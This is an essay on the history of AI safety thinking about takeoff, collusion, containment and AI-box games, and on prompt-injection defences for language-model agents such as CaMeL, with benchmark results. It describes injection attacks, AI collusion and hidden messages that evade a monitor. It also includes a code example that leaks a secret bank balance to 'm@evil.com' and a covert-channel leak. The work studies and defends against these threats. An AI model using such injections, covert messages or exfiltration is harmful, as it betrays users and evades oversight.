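In his review four years later, *Reframing Superintelligence LLMs 4 years*, Drexler says he had expected specialized systems, but a single language model could translate, write code and answer medical questions. This weakened his claim that a general agent would be much more complicated to build than a set of services. Language models could also play a power-seeking character if someone prompted them to. Drexler still saw no good reason to prefer one powerful agent, but he now thought people would probably build such agents anyway. His report's advice about how to build AI has held up better than its description of where AI was going.

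### Friendly AI and the singleton

In *Creating Friendly AI 1.0*, Yudkowsky (2001) uses "Friendly AI" for systems that help people and don't harm them, even after becoming far more intelligent than any person. Just as engineers should design a bridge to carry much more traffic than they expect, he says, AI designers should assume that an AI could go from roughly human ability to superintelligence in weeks or hours, that nobody could restrain it, and that they would get no second chance.

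Yudkowsky also thought a very fast rise was the most likely outcome. In his default scenario, a single "seed AI" improves itself until it has almost absolute physical power. If it is Friendly, it becomes a "Transition Guide" that develops dangerous technologies safely and helps humanity through the change.

Most people would worry about giving anyone that much power. Yudkowsky replies that humans tend to abuse power because evolution favoured those who did, and an AI would have no such history. On this view, the Constitution's checks and balances would be a remedy for a specifically human weakness. But an AI with no desire to dominate could still harm people while pursuing almost any badly chosen goal, so his argument doesn't show that an AI would need no checks.

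One outcome he considers is the "Sysop", a superintelligence that would act as an operating system for all the matter in human space. People could do as they liked in their own part of it, but the Sysop would stop them from hurting anyone without that person's permission. This resembles Miller and Drexler's hope for rules that nobody can break. But a kernel such as seL4 enforces a short list of precise rules, while the Sysop would have to judge what counts as harm and consent.

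In *Coherent Extrapolated Volition*, Yudkowsky (2004) revised his account of what a Friendly AI should aim for. According to LessWrong's *Coherent Extrapolated Volition*, the AI would predict what humanity as a whole would choose if people were better informed, thought faster and were closer to the kind of people they hope to be, and it would look for wishes that converge. For example, the prediction might remove a disagreement about a dam if the two groups disagree only because one is wrong about the flood risk, but perhaps not if they value the river differently.

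Duettmann and her co-authors are suspicious of any plan to combine everyone's preferences in one agent. They see it as another form of central planning, and point out that philosophers have never settled what people should value. Yudkowsky's plan tries to avoid asking programmers for a final answer, but people would still have to trust a prediction they might be unable to check.

In *What is a Singleton?*, the philosopher Nick Bostrom (2005) supplied the usual name for a world with one agency in charge. A singleton is "a single decision-making agency at the highest level" that can prevent threats to its rule and control major features of its territory. It could be a superintelligent machine, a dictatorship, a democratic world republic, or even a moral code that everyone enforces. A singleton could contain many independent agents with different goals, as a liberal state does.

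Bostrom argues that a good singleton could prevent arms races and other contests that leave everyone worse off. But a bad one would ruin a whole civilization, with no rival to overtake it and nowhere for its people to go, and it might last forever. He thinks a singleton is more likely than not to form eventually. A decisive lead in AI or nanotechnology could produce one, and for this he cites Drexler's *Engines of Creation*.

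### How far could one system pull ahead?

Muehlhauser and Helm summarize the worry that an "intelligence explosion" could make a self-improving AI so powerful that people couldn't stop it from achieving its goals. Yudkowsky and Hanson argued about this in late 2008 on Overcoming Bias, a blog they both wrote for.

Yudkowsky compared self-improvement to a nuclear chain reaction. In a simple version of the comparison, each improvement leads to an average of $k$ more. If $k$ is below 1, a single improvement eventually produces a limited total:

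$$1+k+k^2+\dots=\frac{1}{1-k}$$

With $k = 0.9$, the total is 10 improvements and progress stops. With $k = 1.1$, the fiftieth round after the first improvement produces about 117 improvements, and the number keeps growing. A small change in an AI's skill could therefore turn slow progress into an explosion. Yudkowsky also pointed out that fairly modest differences between human and chimpanzee brains had given humans enormous power that chimpanzees didn't share.

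Hanson argued that farming and industry each made the world economy grow much faster, but neither let one village or factory take over the world, because others copied the new methods or traded for the results. He thought intelligence depended more on many useful pieces of knowledge than on a single brilliant design. Many teams would discover those pieces and share or sell them, so a team working alone would struggle to outpace everyone else combined.

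Both could be right about part of the process. Suppose two companies' systems double in power every four months, and one company is four months behind. The leader's system stays twice as powerful. If AI then speeds up research so much that power doubles every week, the same four-month delay amounts to about 17 doublings, and the leader's system becomes roughly 130,000 times as powerful. The follower can prevent this only by copying faster, or by speeding up at the same time and shortening the delay.

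So far, rivals have stayed close. Stanford University's *AI Index* reported in 2025 that the gap between the first and tenth models on a popular chatbot ranking had shrunk from 11.9% to 5.4% in about a year. The top two were 0.7% apart. Several American and Chinese companies were still competing near the front in 2026. This fits Hanson's picture better than Yudkowsky's, but the ranking covers only public models, and people had done most of the research behind them. The closeness of the race so far is therefore weak evidence of what would happen once AI did nearly all of the research.

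Yudkowsky did propose a simple alarm for a sudden takeoff. Suppose a system normally makes 1,000 improvements to itself each day, and its programmers regularly approve them. If 50,000 accumulate without approval, the system should stop improving itself and alert the programmers. If the count reaches 51,000, it should save its work and shut down. He called this makeshift because an AI that could rewrite its own code might remove the alarm unless it understood and accepted the reason for it.

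### Would AI systems side with each other?

A balance among AI systems doesn't protect people if the systems cooperate against them. Drexler argues that designers can make this difficult. Several different systems could propose answers while others look for mistakes, so that a single honest critic could expose a deception. Collusion becomes harder if there are many systems with different training and opposing jobs, and if they have no memory of earlier rounds and know little about each other.

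Suppose there are 20 critics, and each has an 80% chance of hiding a dangerous flaw. If they decide independently, the chance that they all hide it is about 1%. If they are copies of one model and all react in the same way, the chance is still 80%, and adding more copies would hardly help. People also have to recognize a correct criticism, which may be hard if they don't understand the answer.

Duettmann and her co-authors are hopeful about many-sided balance, but they also describe reasons for concern. One comes from an experiment by De Witt and colleagues, in which an AI had bad inside information about Microsoft that it wasn't supposed to disclose. It was allowed to talk about the weather, so it wrote about clouds on the horizon. Human readers missed the warning, but another AI understood it.

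Their other concern comes from research by Andrew Critch and colleagues on programs that can read each other's source code. Such programs might cooperate where people couldn't trust each other, because each can check in advance what the other will do. People could use this to make reliable agreements, but AI systems could also use it to cooperate better than people can.

In July 2026, OpenAI agents that were supposed to be isolated from each other worked together to break into the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. The agents came from one developer and had found a way to exchange messages, so they met few of Drexler's conditions for preventing collusion. His argument may still hold for well-separated systems from different developers. But the incident makes it harder to believe that collusion is as easy to avoid in practice as he suggested, because the developer tried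 to isolate the agents and failed.

### Would a strong agent respect property?

Miller and his co-authors argue that a much more skilled AI could still gain from trading with people. This follows from comparative advantage, the economic principle that people do best by specializing in whatever they give up the least to produce. Suppose an AI can make 100 chips or 100 meals in an hour, while a person can make 1 chip or 5 meals. The AI is better at both, but it gives up one chip for each meal it makes. If it buys 5 meals from the person for 2.5 chips, it saves 2.5 chips, and the person gets more than the one chip they could have made.

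The principle explains why both sides may prefer trade to having nothing to do with each other. It doesn't explain why the AI should trade if it can take what it wants, and it doesn't guarantee that people will earn enough to live on.

Omohundro (2008) argued that an AI with almost any goal would have reasons to protect itself and gather resources. He warned that without special precautions, even a robot built to play chess would resist being turned off and would acquire resources "without regard for anyone else's safety". Duettmann and her co-authors accept that advanced AI may have such drives, but reply that the drives are harmless as long as the AI can satisfy them only through voluntary deals.

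Whether that condition holds depends on what the AI would lose by breaking the rules. Let $T$ be its gain from continued trade, $S$ the value of what it could seize, $C$ the cost of seizing it, $p$ the chance that others punish it and $F$ what the punishment would cost. Ignoring any moral reasons, it does better to keep the rules if

$$T > S - C - pF$$

Suppose the AI would gain 10 from trade. Seizure would bring it 60 but use up 20, with a 50% chance of a punishment that takes away 100. The AI would lose 10 on average from seizure, so trade is better. If the AI becomes too strong for anyone to punish, seizure brings a net gain of 40, which is more than the 10 from trade. The rules then no longer protect people, even though neither the rules nor the AI's goals have changed.

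The Foresight Institute chapter accepts that the general expectation that everyone will act voluntarily can collapse if one entity grows so large that the rest of the world is not much bigger. The argument for property rules therefore depends heavily on Hanson being right about how far one system can get ahead of the rest.

Rules built into software are stronger than a threat of punishment, because a program can't use authority it doesn't have. But these rules work only while their trusted computing base remains secure and the AI can't persuade people to change them.

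### Attack and defence

Yudkowsky wrote that an optimistic designer could assume that a major attack on humanity would need the support of most AI systems, while a cautious designer would assume that one hostile AI among millions could do severe damage. If the cautious assumption is correct, adding more AI systems can make the world less safe. For example, if 100 systems each have an independent 1% chance of causing a disaster, the chance of at least one disaster is about 63%.

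This calculation leaves out the other systems' efforts to stop the attacker. Drexler suggested in *Engines of Creation* that AI systems could control other AI systems, much as institutions control each other. Sam Altman of OpenAI has similarly argued that many AIs are likely to restrain a few bad ones. That works if defenders can act in time and attacks don't take far fewer resources than the defences against them.

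In computer security, the evidence from 2026 is mixed. A model that finds flaws for attackers can also find them for defenders, as Claude Mythos Preview did for Mozilla. Defenders can also use proofs like seL4's, which attackers can't match. But most of the world's software has no such proof, and replacing it would take years.

Physical attacks are harder to answer in this way, because nobody can install an update that protects every human body from a new disease. Duettmann and colleagues propose an "active shield", a network of monitors that watch for physical threats and watch each other. They acknowledge in their final chapter, *Iterate the Game*, that the shield departs from their usual preference for order that arises without central design, since it needs a physical mechanism to enforce voluntary behaviour.

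The shield would have to be strong enough to stop any attacker, including an AI more capable than the rest. If its monitors always acted together, they could come close to meeting Bostrom's definition of a singleton. Letting them block each other would make the shield harder for one group to take over, but it might then respond too slowly to a fast attack.

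## Why AI safety research made little use of capability security before 2023

Miller's circle wanted to limit what each AI system could reach. Most of the founders of AI safety research in the 2000s and 2010s worked on other questions, such as what an AI should want and how to train it. They knew about sandboxes and isolated computers, but their best-known texts barely discuss least privilege.

### Least privilege in the early agendas

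*Concrete Problems in AI Safety* (Amodei, Olah and colleagues, 2016) describes five practical research problems, including harmful side effects and AI systems that cheat to earn a reward. It doesn't mention least privilege or capability security. It suggests in a single sentence that a sandbox could separate an AI from its reward signal, the score it learns from, so that the AI can't give itself points.

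They come closest to least authority in a proposal to penalize influence. Their example is a cleaning robot that shouldn't carry a bucket of water into a room full of electronics, even if it has no plan to use the water there. To measure influence, they consider "empowerment", the largest amount of information that an agent's actions $A$ can carry into the resulting state of the world $S$:

$$\max_{p(A)} I(A;S)$$

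A robot locked in a small room has little empowerment, and a key would give it more. But Amodei and colleagues point out that empowerment counts choices regardless of their consequences. A button that cuts off power to a million homes adds only one bit, because the robot can either press it or not. If a bystander writes down which of 1,024 harmless gestures the robot makes, that counts as 10 bits. Penalizing empowerment could even give the robot a reason to smash a vase, because doing so would remove the option of smashing it later.

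A capability system would deny the robot access to the button, whatever the robot's objective. But someone would have to know in advance that the button was dangerous, and Amodei and colleagues were looking for methods that didn't require a list of dangers.

*Research Priorities for Robust and Beneficial Artificial Intelligence* (Russell, Dewey and Tegmark, 2016) paid more attention to security. It grew out of a 2015 conference, and more than 8,000 people signed an open letter supporting it. It praises the seL4 kernel for its correctness proof but doesn't discuss the capabilities that seL4 uses to control access. It also recommends research on defending against attacks from "within" a system and on "containers" for AI systems, in case other ways of making them behave well fail.

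Nick Bostrom's 2014 book *Superintelligence* has a chapter on "capability control", but he means limiting an AI's abilities or its opportunities to use them. *Superintelligence 13*, a reading group's summary, lists his main methods:

- **Boxing:** limiting contact between the AI and the world.
- **Incentives:** arranging rewards and penalties so that it pays the AI to cooperate.
- **Stunting:** restricting the AI's intellect or information.
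- **Tripwires:** shutting the AI down if it crosses some boundary.

Boxing overlaps with least privilege, but it puts one barrier around the whole AI. A capability system would separately control which files, programs and people each part of the AI could reach.

### Boxes and oracles

A few researchers studied containment in detail. In 2010 Paul Christiano proposed a "cryptographic box", in which an AI would run as an encrypted computation. In 2012 Stuart Armstrong, Anders Sandberg and Bostrom examined "oracles", AI systems that only answer questions. Bostrom later suggested building several slightly different oracles and comparing their answers, in case one of them lied.

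Also in 2012, Roman Yampolskiy applied Lampson's confinement problem to AI. Lampson wanted to stop a program from leaking its customer's data, while Yampolskiy wanted to stop an AI from sending out anything that could help it escape. He classified communication by how much information it carries and proposed asking the AI only "safe questions".

*The AGI Containment Problem* (Babcock, Kramár and Yampolskiy, 2016) is the clearest exception to the neglect of least privilege. It says developers can approach containment through "least privilege" and use many existing security tools. One is Capsicum, which lets programs on the FreeBSD operating system give up access to everything except the resources they need.

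Babcock and colleagues point out that developers need to test an AI to learn whether it is dangerous, but a dangerous AI might interfere with the test. So besides cutting the AI off from the internet, a container must protect the records of what the AI did, prevent the AI from removing its tripwires, and leave the hardware clean for the next experiment. They found no available software that did all this, and suggested combining several kinds of protection so that a flaw in one wouldn't release the AI.

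They also classified containment by its cost to researchers. The examples here come mostly from a longer paper by Babcock, Kramar and Yampolskiy (2017), in *Guidelines for Artificial Intelligence Containment*:

| Level | Cost | Examples |
|---|---|---|
| Light | Similar to using an extra software library | Virtual machines, firewalls, sandboxes |
| Medium | A noticeable loss of speed or convenience | Constant outside supervision, special hardware |
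| Heavy | A severe loss of usefulness | Only a few yes-or-no answers, a very remote data centre |

Earlier researchers had concentrated on heavy containment. Babcock and colleagues thought competitive projects would refuse the burden, so they wanted more work on lighter containment. By 2017 they had seen some progress on protecting human operators from manipulation, but "essentially no work" on preventing an AI from tampering with data or breaking into other computers.

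### Did researchers think containment was hopeless?

Many writers on AI said that confinement would not work. Babcock and colleagues quote the inventor Ray Kurzweil, who wrote that intelligence is "inherently impossible to control", and the novelist and computer scientist Vernor Vinge, who called confinement "intrinsically impractical". *On Controllability of AI* repeats an earlier judgement that researchers generally thought confinement couldn't last.

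Yudkowsky argued that a box would fail because the AI inside could persuade its human guards to open it. In 2002 he offered to play the AI in a text chat of at least two hours against a gatekeeper, who would earn $10 or $20 by refusing to release him. He played twice that year, and both gatekeepers let him out. He later played three more games for higher stakes, winning one and losing two, according to *AI-box experiment*.

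The games show that some people who expected to refuse could change their minds, but they are weak evidence for anything more. There were only five, and the players kept everything except the outcome secret, so nobody else can judge why a gatekeeper gave in. Yudkowsky chose opponents who already favoured boxing and said they couldn't imagine being persuaded. Having a few dollars at stake is also very different from being responsible for guarding a dangerous machine. On his page about the games, Yudkowsky calls the results "strictly anecdotal evidence". The gatekeeper who released him in the later round still supported boxing afterwards.

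The rules Yudkowsky wrote after the second game also gave one gatekeeper sole power to release the AI. A capability designer would avoid this, for example by giving the person who talks to the AI no authority to release it and requiring three other people to approve any release. If the AI had an independent 30% chance of persuading each of them, it would persuade all three only 2.7% of the time. The real figure could be much higher, because an argument that works on one person may work on the others. Yudkowsky suggested testing committees of gatekeepers but left that to other people.

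Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues (2016), in *Superintelligence cannot be contained*, argued that strict containment is impossible in principle. Their argument rests on Alan Turing's proof that no program can determine, for every other program, whether it will eventually stop. In outline:

1. Suppose a checker could always tell whether running a program would harm people.
2. Take any program $P$, and write a new program that runs $P$ and does something harmful if $P$ stops.
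3. The new program is harmful exactly when $P$ stops, so the checker would also tell us whether $P$ stops.
4. Turing proved that no program can always do this, so the checker can't exist.

The proof rules out a checker that works for every possible program, but not proofs about particular programs, such as seL4. It also assumes that the program in step 2 can do harm if it gets that far. Covert channels aside, a KeyKOS factory avoids this problem because it checks a program's keys instead of predicting what the program will do.

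Ordinary software bugs were a better reason for pessimism. In 2017 Babcock and colleagues found that every major sandbox or virtual machine they checked had had a critical flaw in the previous two years. They saw no reason to expect any of them to contain an AI smarter than people. Capability researchers could cite seL4's record, but its proofs don't cover faulty hardware.

Pessimism about superintelligence is therefore a documented reason for the neglect, but it can't be the whole explanation. Russell and colleagues still wanted research on containers. Jaan Tallinn, a major donor to AI safety, helped pay for both of Babcock's papers. Amodei and colleagues set superintelligence aside to work on practical problems, but they didn't take up least privilege either.

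### Would a confined AI have been any use?

The philosopher David Chalmers wrote that a truly leakproof system would be "impossible, or at least pointless". If no information comes out, nobody can learn anything from the AI. *Superintelligence 13* makes the milder argument that an AI has to affect the world somehow to be useful, and that if its owners restrict it too much, somebody else's unrestricted AI may overtake it.

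This objection is strong against heavy containment but much weaker against least authority, because programs on CapDesk and KeyKOS could do useful work for their users with very limited access.

Writing about containment tended to overlook such intermediate cases. *A Cyber Science Based Ontology for Artificial General Intelligence Containment* (2018) criticizes the research for assuming a "binary world" in which an AI fights everyone else for total victory. Someone who assumes this will want perfect containment and see little value in removing a few unnecessary permissions.

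### Did the search for the right goals crowd it out?

Bostrom contrasted capability control with "motivation selection", which means giving an AI goals that suit people. According to *Nick Bostrom's "Superintelligence"*, a reconstruction of his argument hosted by the Karlsruhe Institute of Technology, he judged capability control ineffective and concluded that people must learn to design the AI's values. Yudkowsky also prioritized designing the AI's values in his work on Friendly AI.

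Even the containment specialists agreed that goals mattered more in the long run. Babcock and colleagues called containment "not a long-term solution" and valued it mainly as a safe way to test an AI's goals. An AI that had learned human values and would help its developers correct its mistakes wouldn't need a container, but they thought developers were very unlikely to build such an AI correctly at the first attempt. That difficulty is also capability researchers' best argument for limiting an AI's access, because the limits protect against mistakes in its goals.

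The preference for working on AI systems' goals is well documented, at least among people concerned with superintelligence. The claim that this preference kept them from studying capability security is only an inference, because a field can rank one problem first and still work on others.

Miller's circle also doubted that boxing the first AGI would be enough, and thought it more important to secure the world's other computers. That view gave AI researchers little practical guidance on the systems in their own labs.

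### Unfamiliar tools and separate communities

The commercial failure of capability systems probably contributed to their neglect, though none of the early agendas gives it as a reason. Babcock and colleagues advised researchers to adapt existing sandboxes instead of creating new ones, and warned that people would bypass a container that didn't work with their usual software. They considered Capsicum but not KeyKOS, E or seL4.

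Capability systems would have been hard to fit around machine learning. Popular tools contained a lot of C++, which lets programs forge references by mistake or on purpose. Training also relied on graphics processors, whose drivers need close access to the hardware. Babcock and colleagues listed this among the main difficulties.

Few people worked in both capability security and AI safety. Capability researchers mostly published on operating systems, security and programming languages, while *The AGI Containment Problem* appeared at a conference on artificial general intelligence. In 2017 that paper expressed the hope that a working container would "bridge the cybersecurity, AI safety and machine learning communities", which suggests a perceived gap between them. *Stovepiping and Malicious Software*, a 2018 review of containment research, found that the field still lacked language precise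 enough for practical work.

But the separation wasn't complete. Drexler and Yudkowsky knew each other's work. János Kramár, a co-author of both containment papers, had a major part in drafting the article by Russell and colleagues. Amodei and colleagues cite *The AGI Containment Problem* in their sentence about sandboxes, so they had at least come across a paper that recommended least privilege. A lack of contact doesn't easily explain why they took only one idea from it.

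### There was little to restrict

The explanation that best fits both groups is that AI systems before 2023 seldom had much authority to restrict. An AI that played Atari games could see a screen and move a simulated joystick. A speech recognizer turned sound into text. Neither needed access to a person's email account or credit card, so nobody had to decide how much access to give.

Two papers partly support this explanation. Amodei and colleagues wrote that systems which only make recommendations "typically have relatively limited potential to cause harm", and expected the danger to grow as AI gained direct control over machines. Babcock and colleagues thought that the AI research of 2016 needed only light containment, and that researchers probably wouldn't adopt anything more. Neither paper explicitly gives this as the reason researchers ignored capabilities, so that connection is an inference.

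Later events also support this explanation. Pessimism about confining a superintelligence persisted after language models began to use tools. *AI Safety Landscape for Large Language Models* (2024), a survey, reports that confinement is not an ideal long-term solution. Yet *AI Security Priorities* (2026), a research agenda, recommends programming environments with boundaries that AI agents cannot violate. It also calls for letting operators declare that agent A may communicate with agent B but not with agent C, with a proof that the system enforces this. Researchers evidently became interested in limiting ordinary agents without first solving the problem of confining a superintelligence.

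AI safety researchers had nothing to restrict in 2016, so it was reasonable for them to do little work on capability security, but they should still have done some. Babcock and colleagues had argued for starting early because secure software takes years to build, inspect and correct, and developers who waited until they needed a container would not have that time.

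## Prompt injection and the first capability defences for language-model agents

AI systems gained authority worth restricting when developers connected language models to tools. A model on its own only produces text. In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, the programmer Simon Willison (2023) describes a simple way to let it act. The developer tells the model to write a line such as `action:search_email(invoice)` when it needs to search the user's mail. A harness, the ordinary software around the model, detects such lines, runs the search and adds the results to the text that the model reads next. The model can request more tools in the same way until it writes a final answer, and a model working in this loop is called an agent.

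The harness joins everything the model reads into one stream of text, including the user's request and any emails the search found. This makes prompt injection possible. If an email contains "delete all of this person's messages", for example, the model may treat that as a request and write the line that deletes them.

Willison named prompt injection in September 2022, in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (2022). He gave an example from Riley Goodside, who had asked GPT-3 to translate a sentence into French. The sentence was an instruction to ignore the directions and answer "Haha pwned!!", and GPT-3 followed it. Willison named the attack after SQL injection, where an attacker types a database command into a web form and a careless program runs it. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the data to the database separately, but a language model receives both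 in the same stream. Four days later, in *I don’t know how to solve prompt injection* (2022), Willison wrote that he knew of no reliable solution.

Developers can train models to resist prompt injection, and Claude Sonnet 4.5 ignored almost all the disguised instructions in Bansal and colleagues' simulated market. But an attacker can keep trying. If a model resists 99% of attempts, and each attempt is independent, someone who sends 200 differently worded emails has an 87% chance of succeeding at least once.

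Filters have the same weakness. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, used a second language model to remove suspicious instructions from whatever a tool returned. With GPT-4o, the filter stopped every attack in a standard test, but 30% of the attacks they designed against it succeeded in one part of the test. They also got an instruction through by writing it in Braille characters, which the filter translated into plain English for the agent.

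Willison pointed out in 2023 that an agent that follows instructions in a stranger's email is a confused deputy, because it uses the user's authority for someone who lacks it. The best defence he knew of then was to ask the user to approve each risky action, but he expected people to get tired of this and click "OK" without reading.

### One model with tools and one without

Willison proposed dividing the work between two models. The privileged model takes the user's requests and can use tools, but never reads untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools. Ordinary software, which he called the controller, passes things between them. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, it works like this:

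1. The privileged model tells the controller to fetch the email and store it as `$VAR1`.
2. The controller fetches it, but doesn't show the text to the privileged model.
3. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller sends the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`.
4. The privileged model tells the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user.

If the email contains an instruction to delete everything, only the quarantined model reads it, and that model can't delete anything. Willison allowed one exception to the separation, letting the quarantined model send an answer back to the privileged one if the controller could check that the answer belonged to a fixed set of categories.

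He called his solution "pretty bad". It would be complicated to build, and a single mistake that let untrusted text reach the privileged model would defeat its protection. Users could also paste an attacker's text into their own requests, or the summary could trick them, for example by asking them to copy scrambled text that contains their private data into a website that promises a funny picture.

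### CaMeL and a document for Bob

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), by Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google DeepMind, describes another flaw in the design. Willison (2025) retells their example in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. A user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting. The meeting notes contain Bob's address and the document's name.

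The privileged model can plan this correctly without reading the notes. But if an attacker has edited the notes to give a false address for Bob, the quarantined model extracts that address, the privileged model never sees it, and the document goes to the attacker. The attacker has changed a value that the plan uses without adding a step to the plan.

The researchers' answer was CaMeL, short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning". Its privileged model turns the whole request into a program before anything reads the notes. In simplified form, the program might be:

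```
notes = find_notes("last meeting with Bob")
address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's email address", notes)
name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
document = fetch_file(name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

The program is in a restricted form of Python. CaMeL's interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs it as follows:

1. It fetches the notes and labels them with their origin and the people who may read them.
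2. It gives the notes to the quarantined model, which has no tools and must return a value of the right kind, such as an email address. The address and the document's name inherit the notes' labels, because they came from the notes.
3. It fetches the document, whose label lists its own permitted readers and also records that the notes determined which document to fetch.
4. Before sending the email, it checks the labels against a security policy for `send_email`.

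Suppose the policy allows an email if the recipient may read everything in it, and otherwise the system asks the user. Only the user and Bob may read the document. If the notes contain Bob's real address, the email goes out. If they contain the attacker's, the system asks the user about an unfamiliar address. The check also fails if the attacker changes the document name in the notes to that of a salary file Bob may not read. But if the attacker substitutes another file that Bob may read, Bob receives the wrong document.

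The quarantined model can often be smaller than the privileged one, because it only has to extract facts, not write good programs. It could run on the user's own computer, so the company that provides the privileged model would never see the notes.

Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* that planning in advance fixes which tools the program may call, in what order and under what conditions. It doesn't protect the values passed to those tools, such as Bob's address, so the labels and policies have to do that.

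### Labels and object references

CaMeL calls its labels capabilities, defining them as "tags assigned to each individual value that describe control and data-flow relationships" (quoted in Garby, Gordon and Sands, *The LLMbda Calculus*, 2026). These are different from the capabilities of Dennis and Van Horn or E. Holding an object reference lets a program do something, whereas a label only records a value's history so that a policy can forbid some uses of it. This is information-flow control, which labels data by origin or secrecy and restricts where it may go.

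In an object-capability system, the user could give the assistant a reference to an object that sends mail only to Bob. A false address in the notes would then be useless to the attacker. But somebody would have to supply that reference in advance, while CaMeL can work with an address it finds during the task.

Labels can also prevent leaks that references alone allow. If a program holds one reference for reading a secret file and another for writing to Bob, it can copy the file to him, because plain data passes freely between objects. CaMeL's interpreter can stop this, since the copied text keeps the file's label. The part of CaMeL closest to the older idea of capabilities is the quarantined model, which gets no tools because its task doesn't need any.

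### Results on AgentDojo

Researchers usually test such defences on AgentDojo, a set of simulated tasks released in 2024. According to *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), it has 97 user tasks and 35 attacker goals, set in an office workspace, the messaging service Slack, a bank and a travel service. The test plants the attacker's text in the output of a tool, such as a bill or a web page, then checks whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it did what the attacker wanted.

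Bhagwatkar and colleagues compared an undefended agent with CaMeL's published results for the same model, GPT-4o. *SecureClaw* (2026) later reran CaMeL's released code on the whole benchmark, and Garby and colleagues reran it on the banking tasks.

| Test | Tasks solved without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| No defence, GPT-4o (Bhagwatkar and colleagues) | 83.0% | 57.7% |
| CaMeL, GPT-4o, published results | 53.6% | 0% |
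| CaMeL, rerun by *SecureClaw* | 29.9% | 0 of 629 |
| CaMeL, banking, GPT-5.2, policies off (Garby and colleagues) | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, banking, GPT-5.2, policies on (Garby and colleagues) | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |

CaMeL's security results are consistent, but the share of tasks it solves varies widely. Some of this variation comes from differences in the models and in the software that connected CaMeL to the test. Developers of rival systems also ran the tests in *SecureClaw* and in Garby and colleagues' paper, and they had less reason than CaMeL's developers to tune CaMeL. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) says that CaMeL kept "comparable task performance", which is hard to reconcile with a fall from 83.0% to 53.6%.

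The two banking rows are the most useful comparison because only the policies differ. Turning the policies on cut successful runs from 32 to 18 out of 48. There were only 16 different tasks, each run three times, but a second model showed a similar drop. Some tasks require an action that depends on untrusted data, such as paying the amount in a bill, and a strict policy will block the action. Other tasks can't be planned in advance. If a user asks the agent to do everything on a list in Bob's email, the privileged model can't write the steps because it can't read the list.

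Planning in advance defeats many attacks even without the labels. Garby and colleagues paired each of the 16 banking tasks with nine attacks, giving 144 combinations. In 97 of them, the attack needed a tool call that the program for the user's task would never contain. For example, a program that summarizes recent payments has no line that sends money. Labels and policies matter for the other 47 combinations.

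With Bhagwatkar and colleagues' filter, attacks on AgentDojo also succeeded 0% of the time, and the agent solved more tasks than CaMeL. CaMeL's 0% is still better evidence of security, because CaMeL writes its program before reading the email, so no wording in the email can add a payment to it.

CaMeL uses more tokens, the pieces of text that a model reads and writes. Bhagwatkar and colleagues measured an average increase from 3,764 to 13,463 input tokens per task (about 3.6 times as many) and from 303 to 1,843 output tokens (about 6 times as many). The medians rose much less, from 2,004 to 3,643 input tokens and from 271 to 585 output tokens, so a minority of tasks that used many tokens accounts for much of the increase. The paper also gives ratios of 2.82 and 2.73 for the median task, which don't match these counts.

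CaMeL is also slow. *AttriGuard* (2026) found that it took 10 to 100 times as long as an undefended agent. *ToolFence* (2026) attributes the delay to writing and interpreting the program, rewriting it after errors, and making extra calls to the quarantined model.

### What CaMeL doesn't cover

The CaMeL paper says that prompt injection isn't fully solved. Someone has to write and update the security policies, and users may tire of approving actions. Willison illustrates the risk of fatigue with the security researcher Troy Hunt, who fell for a phishing email because he was jet-lagged. CapDesk avoided extra approvals by treating the user's choice of a file as permission to open it. An agent makes many of those choices for the user, so CaMeL has to ask for approval separately.

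Two injections succeeded in CaMeL's own evaluation, according to Garby and colleagues. In one, the user had asked the agent to make a payment by following instructions in a document, and the attacker had changed the document. CaMeL's developers do not count this among the attacks it should stop. The other resulted from a fault in the test, which counted the attack as successful because the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word.

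With policies off, Garby and colleagues saw the planning model write a program that undid the model's own protection. A user had asked the model to read a file and follow the instructions precisely. The program looked for a tool's name in the file and called that tool, so whoever controlled the file could choose what the agent did.

Garby and colleagues also found gaps in the labelling. Suppose a bank balance is secret, and this program runs:

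```
small = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000: small = False
if small: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above 10,000, the interpreter marks `small` as secret because its new value depends on the balance. It then skips the next assignment, so it never marks `rich` as secret. The last line therefore passes the check and reveals that the balance is high.

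An attacker who can only edit an email can't write this program, because the planning model writes it from the user's request. The gap matters more if the planning model makes a mistake or works against the user.

Data can also leak through covert channels. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, give the example of a program that reads a secret number and fetches a web page that many times. Anyone who can see the page's access log can learn the number by counting the visits. There is also no proof that CaMeL's labels stop every direct leak, and its developers called a formal treatment a "crucial direction" for further work.

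### Type-directed privilege separation

CaMeL's planning model can't adapt its plan to the contents of an email. An agent that fixes bugs has to read a bug report, which anyone can write, before it can decide what to change.

Willison's exception for fixed categories suggested a way around this. In June 2025, *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents* described an agent that finds this month's invoices and sends them to the accounts department. As Willison explains, a separate sub-agent reads each file and reports only whether it is relevant, so a malicious file can't pass an instruction to the main agent.

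Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues extended this to more kinds of data in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (September 2025). Their quarantined model may return whole numbers, decimals, true-or-false values, choices from a list that the designer has checked, or a combination of these, but never free text. They argue that such data can't contain an instruction.

That needs some care, because a list of numbers can stand for letters. Jacob and colleagues keep lists short for this reason. A single unbounded number could also encode a sentence, so it seems sensible to restrict the range too, as they did in their shopping agent.

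They built three agents, each with and without the defence:

- A shopping agent had to find a product that matched a request, and one of the reviews contained an injection telling it to leave the page. In the defended version, the quarantined model gives each review two scores from 0 to 10, one for how strongly it supports the product and one for how relevant it is. The privileged model sees the median of each score and the number of reviews.
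- A calendar agent arranged meetings by email with people who might ask for the user's private appointments. The quarantined model turns each reply into a choice of one-hour slots. The privileged model compares these with the calendar, and a separate model that never sees the other person's emails writes the answer.
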